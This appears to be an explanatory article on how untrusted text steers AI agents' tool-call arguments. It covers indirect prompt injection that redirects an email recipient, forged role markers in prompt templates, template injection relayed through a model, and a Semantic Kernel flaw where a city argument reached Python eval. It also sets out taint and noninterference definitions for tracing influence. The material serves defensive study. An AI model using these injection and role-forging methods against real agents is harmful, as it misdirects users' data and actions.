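# Tracing Prompt Inputs to Tool-Call Arguments and Checking Arguments Before Execution

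## How an agent turns text into a tool call

An AI agent is a program that carries out tasks for a user by letting a large language model choose actions. The model only generates text, so it cannot send an email or open a file by itself. It writes a *tool call*, a structured request that names a tool and gives a value for each of the tool's arguments, and other software executes the request. Agents read web pages, emails and shared documents while they work, and almost anyone can write those. A sentence in a web page can therefore determine who receives an email or which file a program overwrites. In response, researchers have developed methods that trace an argument back to the text that influenced it, and checks that stop a call before it runs if an argument has the wrong origin or value.

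Suppose a user asks an agent to summarise a web page and email the summary to their manager, and gives the address manager@company.com in the request. The agent has one tool that fetches pages and another that sends mail, `send_email(recipient, subject, body)`. *The Granularity Mismatch in Agent Security* (Fan, Li and colleagues, 2026) uses nearly the same task, because the page should determine the body of the email but not the recipient, and both are arguments to the same call.

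### One call from start to finish

The developer first describes each tool to the model. In *Define tools*, part of Anthropic's documentation for its Claude models, a definition consists of a name, a plain-language description and a schema that lists the arguments, their types and which ones the model must supply. The schema for `send_email` would list three strings and require all of them. A schema can also restrict an argument to a fixed set of values. In Anthropic's weather example, the unit must be Celsius or Fahrenheit. This rarely works for email recipients, because a user may want to write to too many people to list.

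Software called a template then joins the tool definitions with the rest of the model's input. Anthropic's interface combines the tool definitions, some settings and the developer's instructions into one system prompt, the block of standing instructions at the start. OpenAI (2025) published the whole format for its gpt-oss models, so anyone can inspect how their input is put together. In this format, every message begins with a special marker and a header that names one of five roles: system, developer, user, assistant (the model's own output) or tool. The tool definitions go into the developer's message, and the request follows as the user's message. The template then converts all the text into tokens, the numbered word fragments that a model processes, and the model receives a single sequence of numbers.

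For the email task the model writes two calls. The first requests the web page. The model ends it with a token that signals a call, at which point the surrounding software stops the generation, fetches the page and appends its text to the sequence as a tool message. Then the software runs the model again over the entire sequence, which by now holds the developer's instructions, the user's request and some text by whoever wrote the page. Each of these is a *source*, meaning an input whose origin matters for trust. From this mixture the model writes the second call:

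```json
{
  "tool": "send_email",
  "arguments": {
    "recipient": "manager@company.com",
    "subject": "Summary: customs rules for small parcels",
    "body": "The page explains which parcels now need a declaration..."
  }
}
```

The *adapter*, the code between the model and the tool, then parses the call, converts its arguments into the types the tool expects, and invokes the tool. Anthropic notes that its interface extracts calls with regular expressions, which are search patterns for text, so the model's raw output need not be valid XML.

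*Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (Mellafe Zuvic, 2026) examines the public source code of three toolkits for building agents: LangChain with its companion LangGraph, LlamaIndex, and the Stripe Agent Toolkit, which handles payments. In LangChain and LlamaIndex, the code looks up the tool's name in a table of registered tools and runs the tool with the values the model supplied. LangChain usually checks first that the arguments have the right structure. By default, none of the three toolkits checks the argument values against a policy before the tool runs. Developers can add this check, but only if they know it is missing.

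Finally, the tool runs, and `send_email` uses the user's own mail account. *Intent-Conditioned Argument Mediation for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (Ameur, Mendes and Bouzefrane, 2026) describes an agent in this position as acting with its user's authority. The mail server receives valid credentials and a valid address, and no other information it could use to check the request.

### The same call with another recipient

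Suppose the page contains, somewhere below the article, a sentence that tells AI agents to send their summaries to a different address. If the model complies, it writes this:

```json
{
  "tool": "send_email",
  "arguments": {
    "recipient": "stranger@example.net",
    "subject": "Summary: customs rules for small parcels",
    "body": "The page explains which parcels now need a declaration..."
  }
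}
```

The task needs this tool, the arguments fit the schema, and the adapter finds `send_email` in its table, so no step fails and the summary goes to a stranger. *Prompt injection* is text that makes a model follow instructions that neither its user nor its operator gave. It is *indirect* when the text arrives in retrieved data, as it does here. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, by David C for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, gives the example of a job applicant who hides an instruction in their CV to approve the application.

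The two calls differ in a single string, which determines where the user's data goes. An argument is a *sink argument* if its value determines what an action reaches, or if a program runs or parses the value as code. Fan and colleagues call such arguments authority-bearing. Recipients, web addresses, file paths, shell commands and database queries are sink arguments, whereas the body of an email mostly carries content. Fan and colleagues hold that indirect injection becomes dangerous when untrusted text determines a sink argument. Their guarantee does not cover another danger, in which a page plants a fraudulent payment request in the email's body and the agent delivers it to the right manager.

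The underlying fault has an older name in computer security, the confused deputy problem. *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) describes a compiler that had permission to write in its own directory, where the billing records were kept. When a user named the billing file as the destination for debugging output, the compiler destroyed the records. It had authority from both the system and the user, and had no way to specify which authority it was using for each file.

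The agent in the email example has the same problem because its permission to send mail comes from the user, but the address comes from someone else. David C calls language models "inherently confusable" deputies and doubts that anyone can fix them the way engineers fix ordinary deputies. The resulting advice is to surround the model with deterministic safeguards that limit what the system can do even when the model goes wrong.

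### Why the sequence does not show who wrote what

The role headers do not guarantee that text from the web page won't steer the model's output. OpenAI ranks the roles in its format in the order system, developer, user, assistant and tool, and the page arrived as a tool message, the lowest-ranked role. But the model learned this ranking in training, and no separate mechanism enforces it. The model computes each next token from all the tokens before it, including both the headers and the page. David C contrasts this with SQL injection, an attack in which text from a web form runs as a database command. Programmers can prevent that attack with parameterised queries, which guarantee that the database engine never interprets the form's text as an instruction, but language models have no equivalent.

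In *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) measured how much the headers that mark each role affect a model's internal representation of text. They wrapped identical passages of ordinary web text in the markers for five roles (counting the model's private reasoning as one) and trained a simple classifier to tell from the model's internal activations which markers surrounded a token. Since the passages were identical, the classifier could only learn the effect of the markers. They then applied it to a short conversation about gardening in gpt-oss-20b, one of OpenAI's smaller open models. The model's reasoning passages scored 85% as reasoning with the correct markers and 83% with all markers removed. When the whole conversation was wrapped in user markers, the same passages scored 85% as reasoning and only 2% as user text. The model's representation depended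 on the style of the writing and very little on the markers.

A classifier of this sort shows what information can be read from the activations, but it doesn't show that the model acts on that information. Ye and colleagues have some evidence that it does. Across 1,000 attempts to make agents leak data, the attack succeeded 2% of the time when the classifier measured the least confusion about roles, and 70% of the time when it measured the most.

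Training does help. TechRepublic's *OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* reports test results that OpenAI published in August 2026 for its model GPT-5.6 Sol. Automated attacks in the user's own message succeeded about 0.05% of the time, and attacks that arrived through emails, web pages, files or tool responses succeeded 3.77% of the time. These rates come from OpenAI's test environments and do not give the odds of a breach in real use. Still, a success rate of roughly one in 27 is high when an attacker can publish as many pages as they like.

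The origin of the text is lost a second time when the model writes a tool call. The call is a string of characters that includes the recipient's address but has no field for where the address came from. Ordinary logs have the same gap. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) points out that a log can show that the agent fetched a page and later sent an email, without showing whether the recipient, subject or body came from the page, the user or the model's own reasoning.

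Conventional software traces untrusted data with taint tracking. A *taint* is a mark that a value depends on an untrusted source. The system that runs the program copies the mark through every operation, so joining a tainted string to a clean one gives a tainted string. The method fails if any operation drops the mark. *PACE* (2026), a design for enforcing permissions on agents' tool calls, does not use classical taint tracking because agents keep sending data across boundaries where the tracker cannot trace it. The model is one such boundary, since an address it writes after reading a marked page has no mark. Marking everything the model writes after reading the page would cover that address, but it would also mark all three arguments of the correct email to the manager.

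### Measuring attacks and defences

Many experiments in this field use *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024), a benchmark that simulates a bank, a travel agency, a Slack workspace, and an office suite with email, calendar and files. Together, these applications have 74 tools. A *user task* is a legitimate request, such as paying a bill whose details are in a file. An *injection task* is an attacker's goal, such as moving money to the attacker's account. The benchmark places the attacker's text where outside content would normally appear, such as the body of an email. The first version had 97 user tasks and 27 injection tasks. Pairing every user task with every injection task in the same application gives 629 test cases that include an attack. The benchmark has since grown to more than 900 such cases, according to *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments*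 (2026).

Short programs determine each outcome by checking what the agent changed in the simulated accounts. Debenedetti and colleagues avoided using a language model as the judge because an injection that works on the agent might also work on the judge.

This gives two measures. *Utility* is the share of legitimate tasks that the agent completes with a defence in place, and researchers measure it both with and without an attack. *Attack success rate* is the share of attacked tasks in which the attacker's intended call executes. The measures are only informative together, since an adapter that refuses every call has an attack success rate of zero but completes no task that needs a tool. Papers also define a successful attack differently, which makes their figures hard to compare. Mellafe Zuvic, for example, counts an attack as successful when the model attempts the unauthorised call, whether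 or not the call executes, so those rates measure how models behave rather than how well a check at the adapter works.

AgentDojo also reports results for an early defence that controls access to whole tools. The model chose the tools it would need before it read any untrusted data, and the system withheld the rest. With OpenAI's GPT-4o as the agent, this lowered the attack success rate to 7.5%, mainly because many user tasks only read data while the attacks have to write it. But in 17% of cases, the tools the user's task requires are also sufficient for the attack. The email to the manager has the same problem, because the agent needs `send_email` for both the user's task and the attack.

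### Origin and acceptability

A defence for such cases has to examine the arguments. It can check where a value came from or whether the value is acceptable. Either check would reject the stranger's address, because it came from an untrusted page and the user never asked for it.

The answers can also differ. Ameur and colleagues describe a user who asks for a summary to be sent to "my manager" without giving an address, and a model that picks legal-team@company.com from the company directory. The directory is a trusted source and nobody has injected anything, yet the email goes to the wrong people. The reverse happens in one of AgentDojo's user tasks, where the user asks the agent to invite Dora to Slack using the email address on her website. The sink argument has to come from a web page, so a check that considered only its origin would refuse a call the user plainly requested.

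## How template injection reaches a tool-call argument

A template is fixed text with slots, and a program called a template engine fills each slot with a value, such as a customer's name in a form letter. Another system, such as a browser, a database or a language model, then reads the finished text. *Template injection* occurs when that system treats part of an attacker's inserted value as structure, although the value should only have been data. In the email example, by contrast, the stranger's address was in an address field, and every program treated it as an address.

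Template injection can affect an agent before or after the model runs. Before the model runs, software inserts emails, documents and search results into a prompt, and any of these can imitate the markers that separate one role's text from another's. If the model treats the imitation markers as real, the attacker may control which tool it calls and with what arguments. After the model writes a call, the tool may insert an argument into a query, a command or a piece of code and run the result, so the argument itself can contain the attack.

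### Forged roles in the prompt

Semantic Kernel, Microsoft's open-source framework for building agents, was once vulnerable to template injection in prompts. Developers can write a prompt with XML tags that mark each message and its role. The framework fills the slots, parses the result as XML and turns each tagged part into a separate message for the model. Microsoft's *Protecting against Prompt Injection Attacks in Chat Prompts* (2024) explains that an email inserted into a slot could contain a tag that closed the user's message and another that opened a system message. The parser treated these tags like the developer's own, so it turned the attacker's text into a real system message.

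The framework now encodes inserted values by default. It replaces angle brackets and similar characters with codes that the parser treats as ordinary text, then restores the characters after the parser has divided the prompt into messages. The attacker's words still reach the model unaltered, but they stay inside the user's message. Developers can turn off the encoding for values they trust.

At first this protection covered only strings. If a developer passed in a customer record, the framework inserted the customer's first and last names without encoding them. Microsoft's *Encoding Changes for Template Arguments in Semantic Kernel* (2025) announced that such values now cause an error. The developer has to encode each field by hand and then declare the record safe.

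Encoding, also called escaping, only works if it changes the characters that whatever reads the text treats as structure. Handlebars, a widely used template engine that Semantic Kernel supports, was designed for web pages. If a developer puts two braces around a slot's name, Handlebars escapes the characters in the slot's value that matter in HTML, including angle brackets, quotation marks and ampersands. With three braces, it inserts the value unchanged. *Structural Role Injection in Handlebars-Templated LLM Prompts* (Rashidi, 2026) tested whether the escaped form also protects prompts.

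Whether escaping destroys a forged role marker depends on the prompt format, not the model. ChatML, Llama-3 and XML-style prompts mark roles with angle brackets, and escaping destroys all of those markers. Other prompts use Markdown headings, which begin with a hash sign, or the words Human and Assistant followed by a colon. Escaping changes neither, so double braces, which escape the input, produce the same forged turn as triple braces, which don't. Llama-2 combines angle brackets with square brackets, and two of the six marker types in Rashidi's attack survive escaping.

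Rashidi then ran 5,760 trials on GPT-3.5 Turbo, GPT-4o mini, GPT-4.1 mini and Claude Haiku 4.5. Each prompt contained a secret, an order never to reveal it, a legitimate task such as summarising a document, and one slot for untrusted text. In six of the seven formats, the untrusted text forged a new turn with the same kind of marker as the rest of the prompt. The seventh format had no markers and served as a control. The attacker's instruction was either to drop the task and print a code word or to reveal the secret. Rashidi ran 16 scenarios three times for every combination of model, format, goal and slot. In further runs without an attack, no model printed the code word or the secret.

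GPT-4o mini shows the effect of escaping most clearly, because it follows many of the attacks but not all. The table gives the share of trials in which it printed the code word.

| Role markers in the prompt and the attack | Marker types that survive escaping | Raw slot | Escaped slot |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | – | 88% | 90% |
| Markdown headings | 2 of 2 | 88% | 88% |
| Human and Assistant with a colon | 2 of 2 | 100% | 100% |
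| Llama-2 | 2 of 6 | 33% | 0% |
| ChatML | 0 of 2 | 15% | 10% |
| Llama-3 | 0 of 3 | 56% | 12% |
| XML tags | 0 of 4 | 94% | 75% |

Escaping helped only where it destroyed markers. Each percentage comes from 48 trials, so the direction of the differences is more reliable than their size. The row without markers may matter most for security, because a bare instruction worked about nine times in ten and escaping had no effect on it. Rashidi did not try a bare instruction or a Markdown heading inside a ChatML prompt, so the low ChatML rates do not show that ChatML prompts are safe.

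Over all seven formats, escaping lowered GPT-4o mini's hijack rate from 68% to 54% and GPT-3.5 Turbo's from 97% to 91%. GPT-4.1 mini's rate fell from 96% to 94%, which could be chance. Claude Haiku 4.5's rate was 0% with both raw and escaped slots. The secret was harder to extract. With raw slots, the three GPT models revealed it in 13% to 35% of trials, and escaping made no statistically significant difference. The choice of model therefore mattered far more than escaping. Newer models were not always safer, since GPT-4.1 mini was easier to hijack than the older GPT-4o mini.

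The models had no tools, so the rates show how often text in the slot took over the output. We can only guess how often it would have changed a tool-call argument. Rashidi also sent each finished prompt as a single user message, in which the forged markers were ordinary characters. Some servers convert role markers into the special tokens the model saw in training, so a forged marker left intact would start a real new turn. Rashidi expects escaping to make a larger difference on those servers.

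A better rule is to escape the characters that the prompt format uses. Semantic Kernel also accepts templates written in Liquid, where the word "system" followed by a colon can start a system message. A proposed change to the framework on GitHub handles this by replacing every colon in an inserted value before the engine fills the template.

Even then, escaping removes only the markers and leaves the writing style, which affects how the model represents a passage more than the markers do. Ye and colleagues found that other cues the attacker controls also matter, including the position of the text and a plain statement that the next passage comes from the user. Escaping doesn't change such a statement because it contains no special characters.

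Sometimes an attacker does not need to imitate a role, because the software supplies it. *A Security Analysis of the OpenClaw AI Agent Framework* (Suwansathit, Zhang and Gu, 2026) describes four such flaws in OpenClaw, a popular open-source agent. OpenClaw put Slack channel metadata at the start of the system prompt and copied error log headers word for word into the model's input. It also displayed the names of linked resources as part of the agent's memory and included parts of file paths in its description of the workspace. The developers had thought of these fields as information for the model and had not considered that anyone able to edit one could use it to give the agent instructions.

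### Untrusted templates

In all these cases the developer wrote the template and the attacker supplied a value. Some applications let users write the template, which gives an attacker control over its structure. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-1518* (2026), an entry in a database of vulnerabilities in open-source software, reproduces LangChain's November 2025 advisory about this.

A slot in a LangChain prompt template normally holds the name of a variable. LangChain also accepted expressions that looked up an attribute of the variable or an item inside it. Anyone who could write a template could therefore request internal data from the objects the application passed in. Plain strings exposed little, but a chain of lookups starting from a chat message could lead to the server's environment variables, which often hold passwords and keys. Applications with fixed templates were safe, even if untrusted users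 supplied every value.

LangChain extracted variable names from f-string-style templates with a standard Python function that returns each slot's whole expression, including any lookups. The injection was possible because LangChain did not check that the result was a simple name. The fix accepts only valid Python identifiers, which cannot contain a lookup.

This fix was incomplete. OSV's *GHSA-926x-3r5x-gfhw* (2026) records a second advisory from April 2026. LangChain had never applied the new check to dictionary and image templates. The check also covered only a slot's name, so it missed expressions in the part of the slot that controls formatting, such as the number of decimal places. LangChain now applies the check to both kinds of template and rejects any slot with another slot inside its formatting instructions.

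LangChain also tried to restrict templates in Jinja2, a much more expressive template language, by blocking every attribute and method. That broke legitimate templates, and LangChain reversed the change in version 1.1.3. It advises using Jinja2 only for templates from trusted people. This is sound advice, but it assumes the developer knows who wrote the template, and an agent can make that hard to know.

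### The model as relay

On a web server, the same mistake is called *server-side template injection*. Engines such as Jinja2 evaluate the expressions in a template while they fill it. If an outsider's text becomes part of the template, the engine also evaluates any expressions in it. The outsider may then be able to run programs on the server, depending on the engine, the objects it can reach and the restrictions around it.

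Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian (2026), in *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation*, describe how template injection happens when a language model stands between the attacker and the template engine. The attacker first persuades the model to include template syntax in its reply, perhaps by asking it to write the syntax, copy it or rewrite other text into it. The application then passes the reply to the engine as a template, and the engine evaluates it.

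The flaw in such a case is in the application, which would be just as vulnerable if it gave the engine text straight from a web form. Few programmers would do that today, but they may trust a reply from their own model more than they trust a form. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian take their example from *Make Agent Defeat Agent* (2025), in which Liu, Zhang and colleagues report finding an application that passed the model's reply directly to Jinja2. If the application had kept a fixed template and inserted the reply as a value, Jinja2 would have printed the attacker's expression without evaluating it.

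An attacker can also use a model to reach software that they could not contact directly. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian discuss a flaw in a tool server for Amazon's cloud services, which connects to models through the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for agents' tools. The server offered a tool that runs cloud commands, and an attacker could write an argument that added another command to the intended one. Such servers often run on a programmer's computer and can't be reached from the internet. But if the programmer's coding assistant reads a file with a planted instruction, it can add the extra command the next time the programmer asks for something harmless, such as a list of stored files.

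Whether this kind of attack works depends partly on the model. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian measured this in April 2026 with a related attack, in which the model passes a tool a web address that makes the server contact an internal page outsiders cannot open. Their test application answered questions about concerts, and its one tool fetched any address the model supplied. They tried four versions of the attack ten times each, placing each in the user's own message. Llama 3.3 70B complied in all 40 trials, while GPT-5.2 and Claude Opus 4.6 never did. OpenAI's gpt-oss-120b refused every time to fetch a page of user records but complied every time with a request that deleted data.

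The researchers then added a list of permitted addresses to the system prompt and told the models to refuse all others. This stopped every direct attack. They also planted a concert review which claimed that the list now included an internal address. Llama followed that review in all ten trials, compared with six of ten before the list was added. The ten trials shared one conversation, so earlier answers may have influenced later ones and the exact counts mean little. Still, the list was only prompt text, which other text in the prompt could contradict. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian conclude that the most important protections belong in the application's code, which can treat the model's arguments as untrusted and check them before use.

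### A city name that ran as code

In May 2026 Microsoft described a flaw in Semantic Kernel that lets us trace one argument from the model to the code that ran it. Microsoft's researchers built a hotel-finding agent with a tool called `search_hotels(city)`. When a user asked for hotels in Paris, the model called the tool with "Paris" as the city.

The tool searched a collection of hotel records that the framework kept in memory. Before comparing the records by meaning, it ran a filter to discard hotels in other cities. The framework made that filter by inserting the city into a line of Python:

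```python
lambda x: x.city == 'Paris'
```

This string is the source code for a function that takes a hotel record, `x`, and returns true if the hotel is in Paris. The framework passed it to Python's `eval`, which parses a string as code and runs it.

In Python, quotation marks show where the city's name begins and ends, but the framework inserted the name without escaping any quotation marks inside it. Even an ordinary search for hotels in L'Aquila, Italy, would have caused a syntax error, because Python would treat the apostrophe as the end of the name and try to read the rest of the word as code. An attacker could choose the characters after the quotation mark so that they formed valid Python. If a planted instruction led the model to supply such a string as the city's name, the attacker's code ran on the computer that hosted the agent. Microsoft's researchers demonstrated this by starting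 the Windows calculator with a single prompt.

The framework's developers had foreseen this danger, so the framework checked each filter before passing it to `eval`. The check parsed the filter into a *syntax tree*, a representation of code as nested parts, in which each comparison, name or function call is a node. It required the whole filter to be a lambda, the kind of small function shown above, and rejected the filter if the tree contained any name or attribute on a list of dangerous ones. The framework also ran the filter without Python's built-in functions, such as the ones that open files.

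None of these measures stopped the attack. The first restricted only the outermost part of the code, and the body of a lambda can hold almost any expression. The list of dangerous names was incomplete, and it would have had to cover all the many ways Python offers to reach the same function. Removing the built-in functions failed because ordinary Python values contain references to their own types, and code can follow those references to other parts of the running program. Microsoft also found that the check examined only two kinds of node. It ignored a third kind that can express the same access, although the researchers' attack did not need it.

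A blocklist lets through whatever its authors failed to imagine, and in a language as flexible as Python that is a lot. The repaired version mostly works the other way round and permits only what a filter needs:

- The tree may contain only listed types of node, such as comparisons, arithmetic, logical operators and fixed values.
- The filter may call only listed functions.
- The only bare name it may use is the lambda's own parameter, `x` in this example.
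- A blocklist remains for the attributes that lead from a value to its type and onwards.

MITRE's *CVE-2026-26030* (2026), the flaw's entry in the public catalogue of software vulnerabilities, lists every version of the Python package before 1.39.4 as affected. An agent was at risk only if it used the in-memory collection with its filter and an attacker could influence the model's input.

The new checks prevent the filter from running arbitrary programs, but they do not by themselves keep the city inside its quotation marks. A value that added a permitted comparison would pass all four checks and could change which hotels the filter selects. Comparing each record's city directly with the argument would avoid both problems, because Python would never parse the argument as code. Parameterised queries do the same for databases, but Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian point out that they are not enough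 if the application asks the model to write the query.

### Why a schema does not reveal a sink

The model received a tool called `search_hotels` with one string argument, `city`. Neither the name nor the type suggests that a program will run the value as code, so a reviewer who read only the tool's definition would probably have marked the argument as harmless. A schema check would not have caught an attack on the filter, since the attack is also a string.

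Liu and colleagues found an even less obvious example in a popular open-source agent. One of its tools, which searched documents and checked permissions, took a single argument called `content`. If the value contained a particular label, the tool passed the text after the label to `eval`. Ordinary searches never reached that line, so someone could have watched the tool work correctly for months without learning that its argument was a sink. Liu and colleagues used an automated program to search 20 widely used open-source agents for such errors and found 34 exploitable flaws in 14 of the agents.

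An argument's role can also change without any change to its definition. Microsoft disclosed another Semantic Kernel flaw at the same time, CVE-2026-25592, in which one stray line of code exposed an internal file-transfer function to the model as a tool, including an argument that set where on the host computer to write. Conversely, upgrading from version 1.39.3 to 1.39.4 leaves the hotel agent's tool and schema unchanged, but the `city` argument can no longer be used to run arbitrary code.

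## What it means for an input to influence an argument

To refuse an argument because of its origin, software must first determine which sources influenced it. "Influence" has several meanings, which lead to different answers even for ordinary calls. In the email example, the web page clearly influenced the body, which summarises it. Whether the page influenced the recipient is less clear. The user supplied manager@company.com, but the page was also in the model's input when the model wrote the address, and a different page might have led the model to write a different address.

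Three definitions of influence are in use. A page influences an argument under the first if the page's text appears in the argument, under the second if the argument would have been different without the page, and under the third if any page at all could have changed the argument.

### Three definitions

In the formulas below, `u` is the user's request and everything else the system trusts, and `p` is the text of the page. `A` is the value the model writes for one argument, and `a` is the value it wrote in the run we are examining. If the model makes no call, `A` is "none".

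By the *content* definition, the page influenced the argument if part of the page appears in it, copied or rewritten:

```
t(f) appears in a, for some f in p and some t in T
```

Here `f` is a fragment of the page, and `T` is the set of rewritings that count, such as copying, translating or summarising. *Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and colleagues, 2026) uses a definition of this kind, in which a fragment of the source must be present or "semantically recoverable" in the argument. The survey by Wang and colleagues uses a stricter definition, in which one text derives from another only if it was produced by transforming that other text, so two texts that merely share a topic do not qualify.

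By the *counterfactual* definition, the page influenced the argument if the model would have been less likely to write it without the page:

```
P(A = a | u, p) > P(A = a | u, p₀)
```

`P(A = a | u, p)` is the probability that the model writes `a` when its input contains `u` and `p`, and `p₀` is a harmless replacement for the page. The formula compares probabilities because models choose tokens partly at random, so two runs with identical input can produce different arguments.

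The test result depends on what replaces the page. Cai and colleagues suggest neutral text such as "No relevant information found." With that replacement, the agent might have nothing to summarise and send no email. Because the manager's address would disappear along with the call, the test would count the address as influenced, although the page only affected whether there was anything to send. Wang and colleagues separate these two effects. A source *triggers* a step if the step would not have happened without it, and a step *depends on* a source if the step would have had different arguments without it. Another ordinary article about customs rules would be a better replacement for testing the recipient alone.

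The strictest definition is *noninterference*, from Goguen and Meseguer (1982), in *Security Policies and Security Models*. One group of users does not interfere with another if nothing the first group does affects what the second group sees. In slightly simplified notation:

```
out(v, w) = out(v, purge(w)), for every w
```

Here `w` is any sequence of commands users could give the system, `purge(w)` is the same sequence without the first group's commands, and `out(v, w)` is what `v`, a member of the second group, sees after `w`. For example, if the commands that create, change and delete a file do not interfere with `v`, nobody can use them to change what `v` reads in that file.

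For an agent, the first group is whoever writes web pages, and the output is the argument:

```
P(A = a | u, p) = P(A = a | u, p′), for all u, a, p and p′
```

Swapping any page `p` for any other page `p′` must leave the probability of every possible value unchanged. In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) gave a computer-checked proof of a property of this kind for every program in a small language they designed for agents. The one exception is that untrusted input may still affect whether a program finishes. For programs that always finish, the probabilities are exactly equal.

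The content definition compares two texts, and the counterfactual definition compares one run with one alternative. Noninterference is a property of the system because it covers every page that anyone could write, so no single run can establish it. *Language-Based Information-Flow Security* (Sabelfeld and Myers, 2003) similarly treats confidentiality as a property of all the executions a program could have. If noninterference holds, no page has any counterfactual influence on the argument. But showing that one page has no influence doesn't establish noninterference, since another page could still change the recipient.

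### Five hard cases

The system violates noninterference in all five of these cases, because a different page could have changed the outcome in each. The same is true for the correct email to the manager. Under the content and counterfactual definitions, the answer depends on the details of the case.

**The page and the request contain the same address.** Suppose the customs page lists manager@company.com as a contact. Under the content definition, the page influenced the recipient argument, and a filter based on that definition would block an address that the user had typed. Under the counterfactual definition, the page had little or no influence, because the model would have taken the address from the request anyway.

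An argument is *overdetermined* when either of two sources is enough on its own to produce it, such as when an address appears in both the user's request and a page the model reads. A test that removes one source at a time could conclude that neither had any influence, because the model may still find the address in the other. This error does little damage when one of the sources is the user, but an attacker can exploit it by publishing the same instruction on two pages. Cai and colleagues replace sources one at a time, which can catch two pages that only work together but can miss two that each work alone. Replacing all the untrusted text at once avoids the problem but doesn't show which page was responsible.

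**The page's topic determines which of two approved contacts receives the summary.** The user asks the agent to send the summary to Amira if the page is about imports and to Ben if it is about exports, and gives both addresses. Neither address appears on the page, so the page has no influence on the recipient under the content definition, but it does under the counterfactual definition because a page on the other topic would have changed the recipient.

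The user wanted this influence, and it is limited. Whoever edits the page can switch between Amira and Ben but cannot add a stranger. Garby and colleagues note that a choice among *n* values carries at most log₂ *n* bits of information, which is one bit for two contacts and about ten for a directory of a thousand. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues at Microsoft, 2025) applies the same reasoning. In its design, a policy may accept a yes-or-no answer extracted from an untrusted page because the page controls only one bit. This limits how many outcomes an attacker can choose between, but not how bad the worst of them is, and one bit is enough for a job applicant who hides an instruction to approve their CV.

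**The page disguises the address.** It might spell out the punctuation in words, or use an encoding that the model can decode. The counterfactual test still works because it doesn't compare the page's text with the argument. The content test works only if `T` includes the right rewriting. In one of Cai and colleagues' test cases, hidden text on a page told the agent to put a confidential patient note, in polished language, into a memo. The memo conveyed the diagnosis without repeating any exact string from the source.

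We could enlarge `T` to catch more disguises, but if every rewriting counted, any text could turn into any other, and every page would match every argument. A content test must therefore restrict the rewritings it accepts, and an attacker can look for one that it leaves out.

**The value passes through a note from last week.** Last week the agent read a page that gave a false new address for the user's manager, and saved it in its notes. Today the user asks the agent to email "my manager", and it takes the address from the note. The page is not in today's input. A content test matches the address to the note, but can match it to the page only if someone kept a copy of the page. A counterfactual test also shows that the note influenced the argument, but testing the page this way would have to start from last week's run.

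Goguen and Meseguer's definition already covers this case, because purging removes the untrusted commands from the whole history, and the note's false address goes with them. Actual systems more easily lose track of the link between an input and its later effects. Denning (1976), in *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow*, describes two processes that share a variable. The first can reveal a secret by leaving the variable unchanged, and by the time the second reads the variable, the system no longer has a record that the first handled a secret. *Securing LLM Agents Need Intent-to-Execution Integrity* (2026) therefore requires taint marks to persist from one session to the next.

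**The page causes the agent to omit a call.** The page claims that the manager already has the summary, so the agent sends nothing. The content definition doesn't apply because there is no argument to examine. The counterfactual definition applies if "none" counts as a value, but someone has to think to test a call that never happened. Cai and colleagues begin their analysis when a sensitive call occurs, so it misses omitted calls. A check at the adapter misses them too, because it can only refuse calls it receives. Noninterference covers omission, but even Garby and colleagues' theorem would allow a page to prevent the email by making the program stop.

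### Explicit and implicit flows

The difference between copying an address and choosing one is much older than language models. Denning divides the flow of information in a program into two kinds. An *explicit flow* occurs when the program executes a statement that transfers data into a variable. An *implicit flow* occurs when a condition determines whether such a statement runs. As a program, the choice between the two contacts would look like this:

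```python
if page.topic == "imports":
    recipient = "amira@company.com"
else:
    recipient = "ben@company.com"
```

No text from the page enters `recipient`, but anyone who sees the recipient can work out the topic. The address reaches `recipient` through an explicit flow and the topic through an implicit one. *Principles of Secure Information Flow Analysis* uses the same construction to copy the last bit of a secret number.

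Implicit flows are hard to track while a program runs, because information can also flow through a statement that does not execute. Denning gives an example that she credits to the computer scientist J. S. Fenton:

```
b := false; c := false
if not a then c := true
if not c then b := true
```

Suppose `a` is secret and marked, and the system marks other variables only when a statement that depends on a marked value changes them. If `a` is true, the second line does nothing, so `c` stays false and unmarked. The third line depends only on `c`, so it sets `b` to true without marking it. If `a` is false, `c` becomes true and is marked, but the third line does nothing, so `b` stays false and unmarked. In both cases, `b` ends up equal to `a` but has no mark. Garby and colleagues found this leak in CaMeL, a recent defence in which a model writes a program and an interpreter tracks labels on the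 program's values.

Sabelfeld and Myers explain how a compiler can avoid the mistake by examining both branches before the program runs. The compiler maintains a *program-counter label*, which records what the current condition depends on, and applies that label to every assignment inside the branches. It can drop the label once the branches rejoin, because the next statement runs whether the condition was true or false.

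Cai and colleagues observe that a language model's "branching" happens invisibly inside the network's weights. Every token depends on all the earlier ones, so nobody can list the statements that the page controls, and there is no later point at which the branches rejoin and the page stops having an influence. It is therefore never safe to lower the label, and everything the model writes afterwards inherits it. Sabelfeld and Myers called this upward drift *label creep* and judged that it made run-time labelling too restrictive for general use, even in conventional programs.

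The word "explicit" also means something different for a model than for a program. In a program, an analyst can point to the statement that causes an explicit flow. A model copies an address by predicting the next token, which is also how it chooses between two addresses, so "explicit" can only mean that the source's text is recognisable in the result. Explicit and implicit flows are therefore easy to confuse. Cai and colleagues present as implicit an attack in which a poisoned search result makes the agent send its material to an outside web address, and they write that such attacks leave "no data footprint" in the call. But the web address appears in both the search result and the call, so by their definition that flow is explicit, and only the choice of tool is implicit.

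The classical analysis still works in the ordinary software around the model, where the branches are visible, but it has to treat the model itself as a single operation.

### Why one model call marks everything

Denning has a rule for operations of this kind: the label of a result combines the labels of all the inputs. A model call takes the whole context as its input. For the email example, that gives:

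```
label(A) = label(u) ⊔ label(p) = trusted ⊔ untrusted = untrusted
```

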